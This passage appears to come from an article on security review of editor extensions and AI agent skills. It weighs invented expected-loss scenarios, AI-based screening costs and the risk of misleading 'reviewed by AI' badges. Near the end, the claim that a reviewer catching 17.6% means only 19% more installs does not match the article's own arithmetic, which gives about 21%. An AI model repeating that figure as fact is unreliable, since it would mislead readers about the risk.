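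An editor extension or agent skill may have no permission list to restrict. Trent recommends running coding agents in containers with reduced privileges and without direct access to long-lived credentials. Datadog Security Labs offers a free monitor for VS Code and Cursor that watches other extensions as they run and blocks operations that match its rules. The monitor can catch something that happens weeks after the test, if it has a rule for it.

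The user must then decide whether the remaining risk is worth taking. Say the converter is worth $10 to them, and a malicious one with access to their bank account would cost them $20,000. One with access only to shopping sites might cost them $200. These amounts are invented too, and the starting risk is again 0.1%.

| What the user does | Remaining risk | Possible loss | Expected loss |
|---|---|---|---|
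| Allows every site, no review | 0.1% | $20,000 | $20 |
| Allows every site after a clean verdict (90% detection) | 0.01% | $20,000 | $2 |
| Allows every site after a clean verdict (45% detection) | 0.056% | $20,000 | $11 |
| Allows only shopping sites, no review | 0.1% | $200 | $0.20 |

If the converter has access to every site, it is worth installing when the reviewer catches 90% of malicious extensions, but not when it catches 45%. The user can't tell from the verdict which reviewer they have. Restricting the converter to shopping sites makes it worth installing with either one. When an extension needs access to something valuable, such as a password store, a clean verdict shouldn't be enough, and someone the user trusts should also have examined the code.

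### When the alternative is no review

Most people don't do any of this, and most extensions get very little human attention. ClawHub grew from about 33,000 skills to 65,000 in three months of 2026. Xiong and Zhang found that 78% of its skills had no stars or comments from users, although 85% of the skills they could read showed signs of using sensitive powers, such as running commands or connecting to the network.

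At five minutes per skill, a person would need about 11,000 hours to read the 134,934 skills that Etteib and colleagues collected. Having DeepSeek read all of them in full would cost an estimated $76, and that method caught 81 of the 131 confirmed malicious skills. People still had to check the skills it flagged, but that meant reading a few hundred instead of more than a hundred thousand.

Even a mediocre reviewer is useful to a store on those terms. One that caught 45% of the 100 malicious extensions in the invented example would let the store remove 45 before anyone installed them. That would protect even people who never read a verdict, and the store could repeat the review whenever a better model appeared.

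The benefit could disappear if a "reviewed by AI" badge made people less careful. With the reviewer that catches 90%, users would have to install about ten times as many extensions to encounter as many malicious ones as they did without review. With the reviewer that catches 17.6%, they would have to install only 19% more. Xiong and Zhang recommend that stores show which scanner produced each result, its version and what it examined, instead of combining everything into one badge.
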